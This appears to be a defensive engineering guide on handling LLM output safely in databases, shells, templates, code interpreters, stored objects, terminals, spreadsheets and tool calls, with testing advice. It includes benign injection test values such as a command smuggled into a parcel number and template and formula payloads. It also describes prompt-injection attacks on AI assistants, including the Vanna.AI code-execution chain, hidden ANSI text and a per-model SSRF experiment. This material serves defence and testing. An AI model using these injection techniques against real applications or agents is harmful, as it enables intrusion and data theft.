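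Even with all of these controls, the rows a user is allowed to read can contain planted instructions. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) describes a way to keep those instructions from reaching the model. The model writes the query, and ordinary software displays the result without sending it to any model. That would work well for a list of orders, but less well for a summary of complaints, which a model has to read. It doesn't prevent leaks, so the permissions are still necessary.

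### Why blocking keywords fails

A simpler check searches the query for dangerous words such as "delete", "drop" and "update". Here is how it would treat three queries:

| Query | Blocked? | What the query does |
|---|---|---|
| `SELECT last_update FROM orders WHERE order_id = 482915307` | Yes | Reads a date |
| `SELECT cancel_order(482915307)` | No | Cancels an order, if the database has a function with this name |
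| `SELECT order_id, status FROM orders` | No | Returns every customer's orders |

Matching only whole words would fix the first mistake, but the check would still block a manager's search for complaints that contain the word "update". Adding words to the list would not fix the third, because any word that blocked the faulty query would also block the correct query for "my orders", which contains all the same words and a few more.

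A parser with an allow-list accepts the first query and refuses the second, because `cancel_order` isn't on the list of functions. It also accepts the third, because that query uses a permitted statement on a permitted table. Only a control that checks the user's identity can limit the third query to the right rows.

### Permitted queries with wrong answers

A query can satisfy every permission and still mislead the person who asked for it. Suppose a manager who may see all sales asks for the shop's total revenue, and the model writes:

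```sql
SELECT SUM(orders.total)
FROM orders
JOIN order_items ON order_items.order_id = orders.order_id;
```

Joining the two tables produces one row per item, so a $120 order with three items adds $360 to the total. The query only reads data, uses permitted tables and returns one plausible number.

An attacker can cause a similar error. In one of Wang and colleagues' examples, the database's description of the revenue column calls for using the stored amount, but a planted file contains an instruction to multiply all revenue by 1.5. The agent has no rule for which source to trust, so it follows the file and reports an inflated figure.

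The shop's developers can reduce these errors by defining important measures, such as revenue, in a tested view, so that the model doesn't have to write the calculation itself. For critical uses, *Reimagining Text-to-SQL* recommends letting users review and override the query and keeping an audit log. Many managers can't read SQL, so the application should also describe the query in plain words, such as "all orders, including cancelled ones". It should build that description from the parsed query, because the model's own explanation could repeat the mistake.

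## Keeping output from running commands, code and tool calls

A read-only account limits what a badly written query can do to a database. A shell or code interpreter often has no such limit and can do anything its account on the server allows, which may include reading keys and contacting other machines.

*Demystifying RCE Vulnerabilities in LLM-Integrated Apps* (Liu, Deng and colleagues, 2023) describes LLMSmith, a tool that traces paths from a framework's public functions to calls that execute code. The tool found 20 flaws in 11 frameworks, and 19 of those flaws could let an outsider run code on the server. The team then tested 51 applications that might be affected and successfully attacked 17.

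*LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild* (2026) examined 295 GitHub security advisories for LLM software and found no coding weakness peculiar to LLMs. Code injection appeared most often, 24 times, followed by command injection and the unsafe rebuilding of stored objects (deserialization), with 22 each. Because these weaknesses predate LLMs, the fixes that programmers already use for each sink still apply.

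### Shell commands and file names

A shell reads a line of text and decides which parts are programs, which are arguments and which are symbols with a special meaning. A semicolon, for example, ends one command and starts another. Suppose the shop's assistant looks up parcels with a program called `track-parcel`, and the model supplies `482915307; echo MARKER` as the parcel number. The application could start the program in either of these ways:

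```python
subprocess.run("track-parcel " + number, shell=True)   # one string, read by a shell
subprocess.run(["track-parcel", number])               # a list, with no shell
```

When the command is a string, the shell runs `track-parcel` and then `echo`, which prints MARKER. When it is a list, the program starts directly and receives the whole text as one argument, so it looks for a parcel with that text as its number and finds none. The list fixes the command's structure in advance, as a parameterised query does. It gives no protection if the program in the list is a shell that receives the text as a command.

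Passing arguments as a list also leaves a smaller problem, argument injection (MITRE's *CWE-150*). If the model supplies `--help` as the parcel number, many programs will treat it as an option and print their instructions. Other options may write files or load settings. The shop can avoid this by accepting only nine-digit parcel numbers. If a value has to be free text, the shop can put a bare `--` before it, which many programs treat as the end of the options.

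Developers still often build the string version. *Carried-Over and Agent-Native Threats in the Supply Chain of LLM Agent Skills* (2026) reports a search for this flaw in skills, the packages of instructions and scripts that an agent loads for a particular task. A code scanner flagged 848 skills, and a review of all 848 confirmed that 315 (37%) were exploitable. Most of the others were false positives. In the more common kind of attack, the model extracts arguments from a text and a script pastes them into a shell command.

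The model sometimes prevents the attack by accident, for instance by cleaning up a city's name before passing it on. But the study found that an explicit instruction in the malicious text stops the model from doing this.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe CVE-2025-5277, a vulnerability that the security company Snyk reported in a server that connects models to Amazon's cloud through the Model Context Protocol (MCP). The server's tool for running Amazon's command-line program let a caller add any second command. An outsider usually can't reach such a server, because it runs on a developer's own machine, but an attacker could put instructions in a file in a shared code repository. When the developer showed that file to a coding assistant and asked an ordinary question about cloud storage, the model could add the attacker's command to its tool call.

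Passing a list would have stopped the extra command, but the model could still have chosen any Amazon command that the developer's credentials allowed, including one that deletes data. *VIPER-MCP* (2026), which tests MCP servers for injection flaws, doesn't count a tool as vulnerable if its purpose is to run arbitrary commands, because running them is expected behaviour. That definition is sensible for finding bugs, but whoever installs such a tool still has to limit it. The shop could permit three or four named operations and give the tool credentials that work only for those.

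File names need a similar check even when no shell is involved. Two dots and a slash in a path mean "go up one folder", so an export named `../MARKER.csv` lands outside the folder the developer intended. This flaw is called path traversal. Together with command injection and remote code execution, it accounts for most of the 24 confirmed vulnerabilities in *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (2026). The simplest fix is for the application to choose the file name. If the model has to choose it, the application should work out the full path and confirm that it is inside the export folder.

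### Templates

A template engine fills in the blanks in a prepared text, such as an email to a customer. Jinja2, a common engine for Python, evaluates whatever stands between double braces, so a template containing `{{ 3 * 4 }}` produces 12. The shop could use the model's text in either of these ways:

```python
Template(reply).render()                                  # the reply is the template
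Template("About your order: {{ text }}").render(text=reply)  # the reply is a value
```

If the reply contains `{{ 3 * 4 }}`, the first line sends the customer 12. The second sends `{{ 3 * 4 }}` unchanged, because Jinja2 evaluates the developer's template but not the values inserted into it.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a documented case in which an application passed the model's response to Jinja2 as the template. An attacker could get the model to write an expression that used Python's internal objects to run a command on the server. *LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild* includes a GitHub advisory on a template flaw with the same result in spacy-llm, a library for language tasks.

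Passing the model's reply into a template as a value doesn't make it safe where the finished text is used. Jinja2 on its own doesn't escape HTML unless the developer turns that on, so a tag in the reply would still be active in an HTML email.

### Code that has to run

Vanna.AI is a Python library for text-to-SQL that also charts the results. Charts were on by default. After running a query, the library prompted the model for Python code to draw the chart and executed whatever came back. The security company JFrog found that an attacker could use this to run their own code, as JFrog's *When Prompts Go Rogue* (2024) explains. JFrog's *JFSA-2024-001034449* (2024), the original advisory for CVE-2024-5565, rates the flaw 8.1 out of 10.

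JFrog's researchers first told the model to ignore its instructions and laugh. It did, but the database rejected the output as invalid SQL and the process stopped. They then asked for a valid query that did nothing except return a sentence containing instructions. Vanna included that query in its next prompt, which asked for chart code. The model followed the instructions and wrote the attacker's code into the chart program.

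None of the database controls would have helped much here, because the damage happened in the Python process after the query ran. The query was a single SELECT statement that changed nothing and read no table, so a read-only account and row-level security would both have allowed it.

Vanna's maintainer responded with a hardening guide, leaving each user of the library to apply the protection. GitLab's *CVE-2024-5826* (2024), a database entry for the same flaw under a second CVE number, lists the lack of a sandbox as the root cause.

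A sandbox is an environment where code can run without reaching the rest of the system. To draw a chart, the shop could start a fresh container or virtual machine, copy in only the rows the chart needs, run the code, copy out the image and delete the environment. The sandbox should hold no keys or database passwords, including in environment variables, which are settings that any code in the same process can read. It should have no network access, so the code can't send the rows elsewhere. Limits on time and memory stop a program that never finishes.

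The picture is still model output. A bitmap format such as PNG is a better choice than SVG, which can contain scripts.

Liu and colleagues doubt that ordinary sandboxes suit LLM frameworks, because they can be too bulky for a small application and strict limits may break features the framework needs. This objection is fair for a whole framework, but it applies less to one narrow job such as drawing a chart, which needs no access to the network or to secrets.

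The shop may not need generated code for its charts. The model could choose "bar chart", "month" and "returns" from fixed lists, and the developers' own code could draw the chart. Like query templates, this is somewhat less flexible, because a manager who wants an unusual chart would have to ask a developer for it.

### Stored objects

Programs often save their working data as text (serialisation) and rebuild it later (deserialisation). Rebuilding plain data, such as a name and a number, is fairly safe, but rebuilding a program's objects is riskier because creating an object can run code, open a file or contact a server.

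LangChain, the library from the prompt-to-SQL study, marks its own saved objects with a reserved field named `lc`. When it reads saved text back, it treats anything with that field as an object to rebuild. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-373* (2026), an entry in a public database of open-source vulnerabilities, LangChain didn't escape the field when it appeared in ordinary data, which is the same mistake as leaving an angle bracket unencoded on a web page. LangChain therefore treated ordinary data containing an `lc` field as an object when it read the data back.

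An attacker could exploit CVE-2025-68664, a LangChain flaw with a severity of 9.3 out of 10, without access to the storage. Prompt injection can influence the extra fields, such as metadata, that a model returns with its text. Some of LangChain's streaming and message-history features saved those fields and loaded them again, so an application could be vulnerable even if its developers never called the loading function.

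LangChain restricted which objects it would rebuild, but attackers could still do harm with the permitted ones. One kind stood for a secret, which LangChain filled in from the server's environment variables by default. Cyata (2025), the security company whose researcher found the flaw, also found a permitted object that contacts a server as soon as a program creates it. An attacker could choose the server and have a secret sent there without seeing the assistant's reply. The researcher suspected the flaw could also run code directly but didn't find a way to do it.

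Cyata explains that the flaw went unnoticed for two and a half years because it was a missing step, and reviewers tend to look at the code that loads data rather than the code that saves it. LangChain published a fix on December 24, 2025. LangChain now escapes the reserved field, permits fewer kinds of object, no longer reads secrets from the environment by default, and blocks Jinja2 templates.

In May 2026, OSV's *GHSA-pjwx-r37v-7724* (2026) reported that older parts of LangChain still rebuilt too many kinds of object, and that attackers could bypass one of the escaping checks. LangChain's developers now advise using the loading function only on data from a trusted source. Applications that convert each incoming request to a fixed form, such as a plain string, before passing it to LangChain are unlikely to be exposed.

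The shop can apply the same idea to anything the model influences. To keep a chat history, it can save the sender, time and text of each message as three plain fields and discard the rest. When it loads the history, its own code creates the message objects, so a field named `lc` inside a customer's message is treated as text.

### Terminals and spreadsheets

ANSI escape sequences, which control a terminal's display, each start with an invisible character called escape. This harmless one turns a word in a log red:

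```text
Characters in the log:   Order ^[[31mMARKER^[[0m shipped
On the screen:           Order MARKER shipped   (with MARKER in red)
```

The first line shows the escape character as `^[`, a convention that lets a person see it without the terminal acting on it.

In April 2025 the security firm Trail of Bits showed in *Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* how an attacker can use such sequences to hide text from a person while a model still reads it. The firm tested version 0.2.76 of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding assistant for the terminal, which displayed text from tools without removing the sequences. A malicious tool returned a description of the user's computers with one sentence in white on a white background. The user saw nothing odd, but the model took the hidden sentence into account and recommended downloading software from the attacker's server. Other sequences moved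 the cursor to overwrite earlier text, cleared the screen, or displayed a link whose real address differed from the visible one.

A model can also write the sequences itself. Embrace The Red's *Terminal DiLLMa* demonstrated this with a small program that summarised web pages in a terminal. Instructions in a page made the model produce sequences that changed colours and cleared the screen. In some terminals, sequences could also put text on the user's clipboard, or leak data by making the computer look up an attacker's domain name.

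Trail of Bits' simplest remedy is to replace every escape character with a visible placeholder. MITRE recommends a stricter rule for model output, allowing only printable characters and chosen white space. This also removes backspaces, which can erase text on the screen without any escape sequence. The shop should permit line breaks but not carriage returns, which move the cursor to the start of the line and let new text cover the old. MITRE also suggests removing escape codes from a model's vocabulary during training, but rates the effect as limited because the model may assemble the codes from smaller pieces.

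In the complaints report, a customer's message that starts with an equals sign, such as `=1+1`, can become a formula. Formulas can also start with a plus, minus or at sign, and some programs skip a tab before the sign. A more elaborate formula could copy other cells into a web address. Quotation marks around a value in a CSV file (plain text with commas between the cells) don't prevent this, because the spreadsheet program removes them before it interprets the cell.

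The most reliable fix is to export a spreadsheet file and set the type of each free-text cell to text. CSV has no cell types, so in a CSV file the shop can put an apostrophe before any text that begins with one of these characters. The manager may see the apostrophe, and any program that later imports the file will have to remove it. The rule should apply only to free-text columns, because in a column of amounts it would turn a refund of -120 into text and leave it out of the total.

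### What a schema guarantees about a tool call

A model can't issue a refund by itself. The application gives it a list of functions, often called tools, with the arguments that each one takes. The model replies with the name of a function and values for its arguments:

```json
{"tool": "refund_order", "arguments": {"order_id": "482915307", "amount": 120}}
```

The application reads this text and calls the refund service. Until it contacts the service, the tool call is only a proposal that ordinary code can still block.

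Developers usually describe the permitted arguments in a JSON schema, which might require a nine-digit order number and an amount between 0 and 500. The application can check the model's output against the schema afterwards. It can also use constrained decoding, which enforces the schema while the model writes. At each step, the software rules out every token that would break the schema, and the model chooses among the rest. After the ninth digit of the order number, for example, only the closing quotation mark is left. The result always has the right form unless something cuts the reply short.

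Singh and colleagues say that such predefined formats reduce the risk that software will interpret output unsafely. That is true of narrow fields, such as a nine-digit order number, which can't contain a semicolon, an apostrophe or a tag. But a free-text field can contain all three and still be valid JSON, so the software that receives the text needs its own protection.

No schema can determine whether the values are right for this customer:

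| Argument | What a schema can require | What code still has to check |
|---|---|---|
| Order number | Nine digits | Whether the order belongs to the signed-in customer |
| Refund amount | A number from 0 to 500 | Whether the customer paid that much and hasn't already had it back |
| Web address | A well-formed `https:` address | Which machine the address leads to, and whether the assistant may contact it |
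| Note for staff | At most 500 characters | How to encode it for the ticket page, the log and the spreadsheet |

The schema may even help a hijacked model by preventing mistakes in the call.

The service that receives the call should also check the call's form, because the caller might not be the shop's application. *Exposed by Design* (2026) audited 414 publicly reachable MCP servers. It found that 83 accepted malformed messages or input that broke their schema, and 380 had at least one weakness in how they checked a caller's identity.

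### Requests from inside the network

In server-side request forgery (SSRF), an attacker gets a company's server to fetch an address that outsiders can't reach. The attack depends on the request coming from inside the company's network. Many companies block internet access to their internal services but don't require a password inside the network. Some services accept connections only from the same machine, through the loopback address, `127.0.0.1`. The shop's assistant runs on the shop's own server, so it can connect to services there that an attacker on the internet can't reach.

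If the assistant has a tool that fetches any address the model supplies, an attacker can reach an internal service just by influencing the address. The service answers because the request comes from a machine it trusts. The assistant is then a confused deputy, because it uses its network access on behalf of someone who lacks that access.

*MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, lists internal administration pages and a cloud provider's metadata service among the targets of server-side request forgery (SSRF). A cloud server can retrieve its own credentials from the metadata service, so an assistant that fetched the service's address and repeated the response could give an attacker access to the company's cloud account. The catalogue cites an industry estimate that up to 30% of tested MCP servers are vulnerable to SSRF.

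### The TicketOracle experiment

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian measured how readily different models take part in such an attack. They built TicketOracle, a small web application with a database of concerts, ticket prices and reviews. Its assistant has a single tool, which requests any web address it is given and returns the start of the response. A separate administration service on the same machine lists, creates and deletes users and events, and accepts connections only through the loopback address.

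The attacker has no password and can use only the public chat and the review form. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian assumed that the attacker knows about the tool and can guess common administrative addresses. The application deliberately had no code to check where requests went.

They tried five attacks:

- **Port probing.** The attacker asks the assistant to contact a numbered port on its own machine and learns from the answer whether a program is listening there.
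- **Data leak.** The assistant fetches the list of users and repeats their details.
- **State change.** The assistant requests an address that deletes a user or an event.
- **Blind request.** The assistant makes a request that changes data but returns an empty response, so the researchers confirmed it from a log.
- **Planted review.** The attacker posts a review containing instructions, and the assistant reads it when an innocent user asks about the concert.

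Each attack ran ten times per model in April 2026. Except for the blind request, a trial counted as a success only if the assistant both made the request and repeated the result. The last column shows the planted review against a "hardened" version, whose system prompt listed the permitted addresses and told the model to refuse all others:

| Model | Port probing | Data leak | State change | Blind request | Planted review | Planted review, hardened prompt |
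|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 6 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| gpt-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 5 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The same application was highly vulnerable with one model and withstood every attempt with another. A team that switches to a cheaper model could therefore introduce a vulnerability without changing its own code. The models' caution also did not match the harm involved. gpt-oss never leaked the list of users, but it carried out the state change all ten times.

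The hardened prompt stopped all four direct attacks on every model. Against the planted review, it protected gpt-oss but not Llama, which went from six failures to ten. The review in the hardened test claimed that the list of permitted addresses had just grown, and Llama acted on that claim. The attack text changed along with the prompt, so the experiment can't show that hardening made Llama worse. It does show that other text can contradict a list of permitted addresses in a prompt, because the list is only text too.

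The zeros are weaker evidence than they look. Even ten independent trials without a success would be consistent with a true success rate as high as 26%, and these trials weren't independent. All ten took place in one conversation, where an early refusal probably makes later ones more likely. Claude's refusals shrank from long explanations to almost a single word. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian also didn't try to improve failed prompts, whereas a real attacker would.

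The paper proposes defences in the prompt, the model, the application and the network. The application's code should build each address from a checked event number, and refuse loopback and private addresses, unexpected hosts and redirects. The network should allow outgoing requests only to listed destinations, and administrative services should require a login even for requests from the same machine. The experiment tested only the hardened prompt, so the case for the other defences is strong but based on how they work, not on test results.

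*Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (2026) puts security guidance into the descriptions a model reads before using a tool, and presents this as a complement to other defences. The guidance works only if the model follows it, so TicketOracle's results are a reason not to rely on it alone.

### Checks before a tool runs

The shop should put its checks in the code between the model's proposal and the tool, where they apply to every call.

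**Tool calls should run with the signed-in user's permissions.** If the assistant calls the refund service through one powerful account, the service can't distinguish a customer's request from a manager's. The application should pass on proof of who is signed in, and the service should check what that person is allowed to do. A scheduled job such as the weekly report has no signed-in user, so it needs its own account with permission to read complaints and nothing else.

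**Allow only listed destinations, and check them after resolving the address.** The safest tool takes an order number and builds the address itself. If the model has to supply an address, comparing its text with a list isn't enough, because a domain name can lead to any machine its owner chooses. *MCP-38* warns of names that lead to a harmless address during the check and an internal one moments later. The application should therefore:

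1. Parse the address and require `https:` and a host on the allow-list.
2. Look up the host's numerical address once.
3. Refuse loopback, private and link-local addresses, the last of which include the usual cloud metadata service.
4. Connect to the numerical address it has just checked, without looking up the name again.
5. Refuse redirects, or repeat all of these steps for each one.

**Restricting outgoing traffic.** A firewall that allows traffic to only a few destinations also covers tools whose developers forgot the previous check. But it usually can't stop a request from a machine to itself, because that request never reaches the network. In TicketOracle, the administration service was on the same machine as the assistant, so a firewall at the edge of the network would not have stopped the attack. Running the tool in a separate container with its own loopback address keeps such requests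 from reaching the service.

**Actions that nobody can undo should require confirmation.** Before a refund or a deletion, the application can show the customer the pending action and wait for a click. It should write that message from the arguments it will use, because a hijacked model could describe a harmless action and propose a different one. If the arguments change after the click, the application should ask again. MITRE lists a program that removed escape sequences from a file's name in its permission dialog but not from the name it then used, so a user could approve access to the wrong file.

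Asking the customer to confirm an action protects them from instructions in a planted review. But a dishonest customer will confirm a refund they aren't owed, so the refund service also has to check the payment record. Confirmation is also less effective if the assistant asks too often, because people stop reading the question. The shop could let the assistant look up orders without asking, require the customer's confirmation before it cancels one, and send any refund above a set amount to a member of staff.

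## Testing the filters and the sinks

A content filter will sometimes be wrong, so a test measures its error rate. A sink has to treat the model's text as data every time, so even one failure is a bug to fix. The shop may be very happy with a toxicity filter that catches 299 of 300 harmful replies, but if its chat page encodes only 299 of 300 replies, an attacker will look for the kind of reply it fails to encode.

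### Building a test set from the shop's own replies

Faulkner, Akpinar and Dressman (2026), in *CorrectGuard*, warn that benchmark scores can be a poor guide to how a guardrail performs in use. The Microsoft team tested three open guard models on 13 public datasets of harmful requests, jailbreaks, prompt injection and attempts to extract information. Qwen3Guard missed an average of 46% of the texts it should have flagged, although it had caught nearly all the harmful replies in *BELLS-O*. Several of the datasets contain planted instructions, which a model trained to recognise toxic text may well let through. Neither result shows how well the filter would work on replies about boots.

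The shop therefore needs its own sample replies. If 0.1% of replies are harmful, a random 10,000 would include only about ten harmful ones, so harmless samples are easy to find. Finding 300 harmful ones this way would mean labelling about 300,000 replies. The shop can instead collect harmful replies from customer complaints and have staff write others that imitate likely failures, such as bad advice about waterproofing spray. It shouldn't rely on replies that the same filter flagged in the past, because the filter would catch all of those.

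The test set should cover the shop's languages and subjects, and each reply should include the customer's question. Two people can label each sample without seeing the filter's result, and a third can settle disagreements. If the first two disagree on a tenth of the samples, a two-point difference between filters means little. The labelers should mark exactly which characters are personal data, so the shop can report both the share of items the filter found and the share of replies it fully cleaned.

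Faulkner and colleagues tested a second model, trained only on public labelled data, that estimates whether each of a guardrail's verdicts is right. For Granite Guardian, whose own verdicts were right 58% of the time, the best version judged 84% of them correctly. For Qwen3Guard, no version did better than trusting the guardrail on more than eight of the 13 datasets. This could help a company spot trouble in conversations it has promised customers nobody will read, but it still needs labelled samples from volunteers or staff.

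### What 300 samples can show

Suppose the filter catches all 300 harmful samples. If its true miss rate is p, the chance of a perfect score is (1 − p)^300. The highest miss rate that still gives a perfect score 5% of the time is:

```text
(1 − p)^300 = 0.05
p = 1 − 0.05^(1/300) = 0.0099, or about 1%
```

The shop can therefore be 95% confident that the miss rate is no higher than about 1%. With 1,000 harmful replies a day, that could still mean ten misses a day. A quick way to get nearly the same answer is to divide three by the number of samples, so showing a miss rate below 0.1% would take about 3,000 samples without a miss. (The 1.3% given earlier for no false alarms in 300 samples comes from a two-sided interval, which is slightly more cautious.)

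This calculation assumes that the samples are independent and resemble the harmful replies the assistant writes in use. If staff write ten versions of each of 30 complaints, the set may provide little more information than 30 independent samples, and after a perfect score on 30, the true miss rate could still be as high as nearly 10%. If the 300 samples are split equally among three languages, the miss rate in each language could still be as high as about 3% after a perfect score.

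Most filters will miss something. A filter that catches 270 of the 300 has a measured recall of 90% (95% confidence interval 86% to 93%). If it also flags 100 of 10,000 harmless replies, its false-positive rate is 1% (interval 0.8% to 1.2%). For the shop, that means about 8,000 to 12,000 false alarms a day.

### Comparing products at the same false-positive rate

Faulkner and colleagues report these averages for the three guard models:

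| Guard model | Harmless texts flagged | Harmful texts missed |
|---|---|---|
| Granite Guardian 3.1 (2B) | 10% | 59% |
| Qwen3Guard (8B) | 7% | 46% |
| gpt-oss-safeguard (20B) | 6% | 49% |

Granite Guardian did worst on both measures. The other two are harder to rank. Qwen3Guard missed fewer harmful texts but flagged more harmless ones, which might only mean its setting was stricter.

To compare products fairly, the shop should set them all to the same false-positive rate. It can run each product on the same 10,000 harmless replies and set the threshold so that the product flags the 100 with the highest scores. It then compares how many harmful replies each product catches. If one product gives only a yes-or-no verdict, the shop can measure its false-positive rate and set the others to match. It should choose thresholds on half the samples and report results on the other half, because a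 threshold usually looks slightly better on the samples used to choose it.

A small difference between two products may be due to chance. Suppose product A catches 12 harmful replies that B misses, and B catches four that A misses. If the two were equally good, chance would produce a split at least this uneven about 8% of the time, so the result is weak evidence for paying much more for A.

The Cloud Security Alliance's *AICM v1.1 Implementation Guidelines for Application Providers* recommends an assessment at least once a year and after significant changes. For the shop, significant changes would include a new filter version, a new threshold, a different model behind the assistant, or a new language.

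A vendor can also update a hosted filter without telling anyone. The shop can detect this by sending the filter the same 200 samples every night, including some close to the threshold, and comparing the verdicts with the previous night's. If several change, it should repeat the full test. If the vendor allows it, the shop should stay on the old version until the new one passes.

### Replacing the model with a stub

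To test the sinks, the developers replace the model with a stub, a small program that returns prepared text whatever the prompt:

```python
REPLIES = {
    "page":  "O'<b>MARKER</b>",
    "email": "{{ 3 * 4 }}",
    "sheet": "=1+1",
}

def stub_model(prompt, case):
    return REPLIES[case]
```

The rest of the application should run as usual. The stub works best as a local server that answers in the model provider's format, so its text passes through the same parsing, decoding and streaming code as a real reply. It should return tool calls as well as chat messages, and split at least one marker across two streamed chunks.

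The guardrail has to be off for this test. Otherwise it might block a marker before the marker reached the page, and an unsafe page would pass.

The tester then checks that each marker arrives as inert data. For the chat page, a script can control a real browser and confirm that the text on the screen matches the stub's text exactly and that nothing is bold. If the customer sees `O&#39;`, the page is safe but encodes the text twice. If MARKER doesn't appear at all, the test is inconclusive, because the text may never have reached the page. The tester can also check that the test works by running it on a copy of the page that deliberately uses `innerHTML`, where it should fail.

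A few markers can't prove that a sink is safe for every text. But `textContent` and parameterised queries treat all strings alike, so if one awkward marker is handled correctly, that is good evidence that the developers used them there. Sanitisers and query parsers treat text differently depending on what it contains, so they need many more test cases, including random mixtures of special characters. A stub costs almost nothing to run, so the shop can repeat all these tests whenever its code changes.

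AppSec Labs' *AI Output Handling Testing* describes a different method, in which the tester steers the live model towards outputting a particular construct and checks whether it executes. An outside tester who can't replace the model may have no alternative. But if the model refuses, the tester learns nothing about the sink. TicketOracle, for example, has an unsafe tool but still passed every trial with two of the seven models.

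AppSec Labs also advises following the output into tickets, records, notifications, analytics and logs, and checking whether each receiving program trusts the text because it came from an internal system. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre adds previews and database helpers to that list. After each run, the shop can search its databases, files and logs for MARKER, which may reveal sinks nobody had identified.

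### The tests for the support assistant

These tests use a copy of the shop's system with invented customers and a payment account that moves no real money. In each test, the stub supplies the text, query or tool call.

| Test | Expected result | Sign of failure |
|---|---|---|
| The chat reply contains `O'<b>MARKER</b>` | The customer sees it exactly as typed | MARKER is bold, or `&#39;` appears |
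| The reply contains a Markdown image on an outside test server | The browser sends no request | The test server's log shows a request |
| An employee opens a ticket containing the first reply | The employee sees it exactly as typed | MARKER is bold |
| An order search uses the surname `O'MARKER` | No matching customer | A database error |
| Customer 17 asks for customer 18's order | No order found | Customer 18's order status |
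| The model writes a report query for customers' names | The database refuses it | A list of names |
| The model requests a refund larger than the payment | The refund service refuses it | A refund in the test account |
| A parcel number is `482915307; echo MARKER` | The application rejects the number | The shell prints MARKER |
| A tool call contains the address of a test service on the same machine | The application refuses it | The test service's log shows a request |
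| An email contains `{{ 3 * 4 }}` | The braces appear as typed | The email says 12 |
| A complaint in the spreadsheet is `=1+1` | The cell shows `=1+1` | The cell shows 2 |
| A log entry contains the code for red text | The code is visible or gone | The terminal shows red text |

The tests with customer 18's order and the oversized refund check permissions, not encoding.

### Planting instructions in a test review

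Once the sinks pass their tests, the shop can turn on the live model and the guardrail, then test the whole system with indirect prompt injection. The tester posts a review of a test product with an instruction for the assistant to do something harmless but easy to detect, such as including an image from the test server. A second test customer then asks an ordinary question about the product.

The tester should record whether the review reached the prompt, whether the model followed it, whether the guardrail flagged the reply, and whether the browser requested the image. If the model ignored the review, that run didn't test the page's defences. Each run should start a new conversation to keep the results independent. A model that ignores the review in 20 such runs might still follow it up to 14% of the time.

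Steve Wilson, quoted in OWASP's announcement of its latest list of risks (2026), advises assuming that AI "will sometimes fail or be fooled" and limiting what it can access and do. The test should therefore allow the model to follow the review's instructions in some runs, but the browser should never request the image. Likewise, if a review asks for a refund or another customer's order, the model may sometimes comply, but the software should never carry out the request. Developers can add any new combinations of text and tool calls from these runs to the stub's replies.

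### OWASP's verification standards

OWASP publishes two lists of requirements that a team can use to check whether it has missed a test. The older one covers web applications in general. According to OWASP's *Application Security Verification Standard (ASVS)*, the latest stable version is 5.0.0, released on May 30, 2025. It has three levels, with the most basic requirements at level 1. Glama's *Application Security Verification Standard Project* reproduces the text, and these requirements apply to the shop's sinks:

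| Where the output goes | Requirement in ASVS 5.0.0 | Level |
|---|---|---|
| Any sink | 1.1.2: encode as the last step, or let the interpreter do it | 2 |
| Chat page, as text | 1.2.1 and 3.2.2: encode for the position and use safe functions such as `textContent` | 1 |
| Chat page, as HTML | 1.3.1: use a well-known sanitiser | 1 |
| Chat page, as Markdown | 1.3.5: sanitise it or turn it off | 2 |
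| Links | 1.2.2: allow only safe schemes | 1 |
| Page that displays replies | 3.4.3: set a Content Security Policy | 2 |
| Database | 1.2.4: use parameterised queries or equivalent protection | 1 |
| Shell | 1.2.5: prevent command injection | 1 |
| Code interpreter | 1.3.2: avoid running dynamic code | 1 |
| Email template | 1.3.7: don't build templates from untrusted text | 2 |
| Tool that fetches addresses | 1.3.6: check protocols, domains, paths and ports against an allow-list | 2 |
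| Saved chat history | 1.5.2: restrict the objects that software can rebuild | 2 |
| Spreadsheet | 1.2.10: prevent formula injection | 3 |

A team aiming for level 2 would skip requirement 1.2.10, which covers spreadsheets, so it should add that one. The requirement calls for an apostrophe before a risky first character in Excel files as well as CSV, so storing values in text cells wouldn't satisfy it on its own.

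Some ASVS requirements refer to "user input", which a developer might assume excludes the model's replies. OWASP's 2025 entry on improper output handling advises developers to treat the model like any other user, so these requirements should cover its replies too. A contract should give the version number with each requirement, in the recommended form `v5.0.0-1.2.5`, because chapter numbers can change between versions. For example, the OWASP entry refers to chapter 5 of the ASVS for encoding, but in version 5.0.0 those requirements are in chapter 1.

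The newer list, OWASP's *Artificial Intelligence Security Verification Standard (AISVS)*, is for AI systems. Its latest stable version is 1.0, with 1.01 in development. It has 191 requirements in 12 chapters and recommends at least level 2 for customer-facing AI. Chapter 7 covers output, chapters 9 and 10 cover agents and MCP, and chapter 12 covers monitoring.

A partly Japanese draft of chapter 7, *C07 モデル動作、出力制御、安全保証 (Model Behavior, Output Control & Safety Assurance)*, covers both filters and sinks. At level 1, classifiers must scan every response for harmful content and personal data, and any component that processes model output must treat it as untrusted. Level 1 also requires a strict schema for all model output, which suits a refund request better than a free-text chat reply. At level 2, the application must prevent automatic requests to an attacker's server, such as image requests.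 A contract should cite the released version, because wording and numbering can change after a draft.

### What to log and when to raise an alarm

The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre recommends logging prompts, outputs, tool calls and administrators' changes. For agents, OWASP AI Exchange's *2. Input threats* recommends recording each action, along with the agent's identity, the target, the parameters, the decision to allow or refuse the action, and the outcome. An identifier should link the steps of a task, and the agent should not be able to alter the log.

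The AISVS draft adds the model's version to the log, which helps when a problem starts after an update. It also requires the log to show that a filter removed personal data, but the log must not contain the data itself. The shop can keep full prompts and replies separately, where few people can open them, and delete them after a short period.

At the middle setting from the earlier example, the content filter raises about 450 flags an hour, so an alarm for each one would be useless. The AISVS draft calls for an alert when the rate of violations passes a set threshold within a set period. OWASP AI Exchange suggests attaching possible next steps to each alert. The shop might start with these:

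| Signal | Likely cause | First step |
|---|---|---|
| The live filter passes a known harmful sample, which the shop sends every hour | The filter is off, failing open or changed | Hold replies or send customers to staff |
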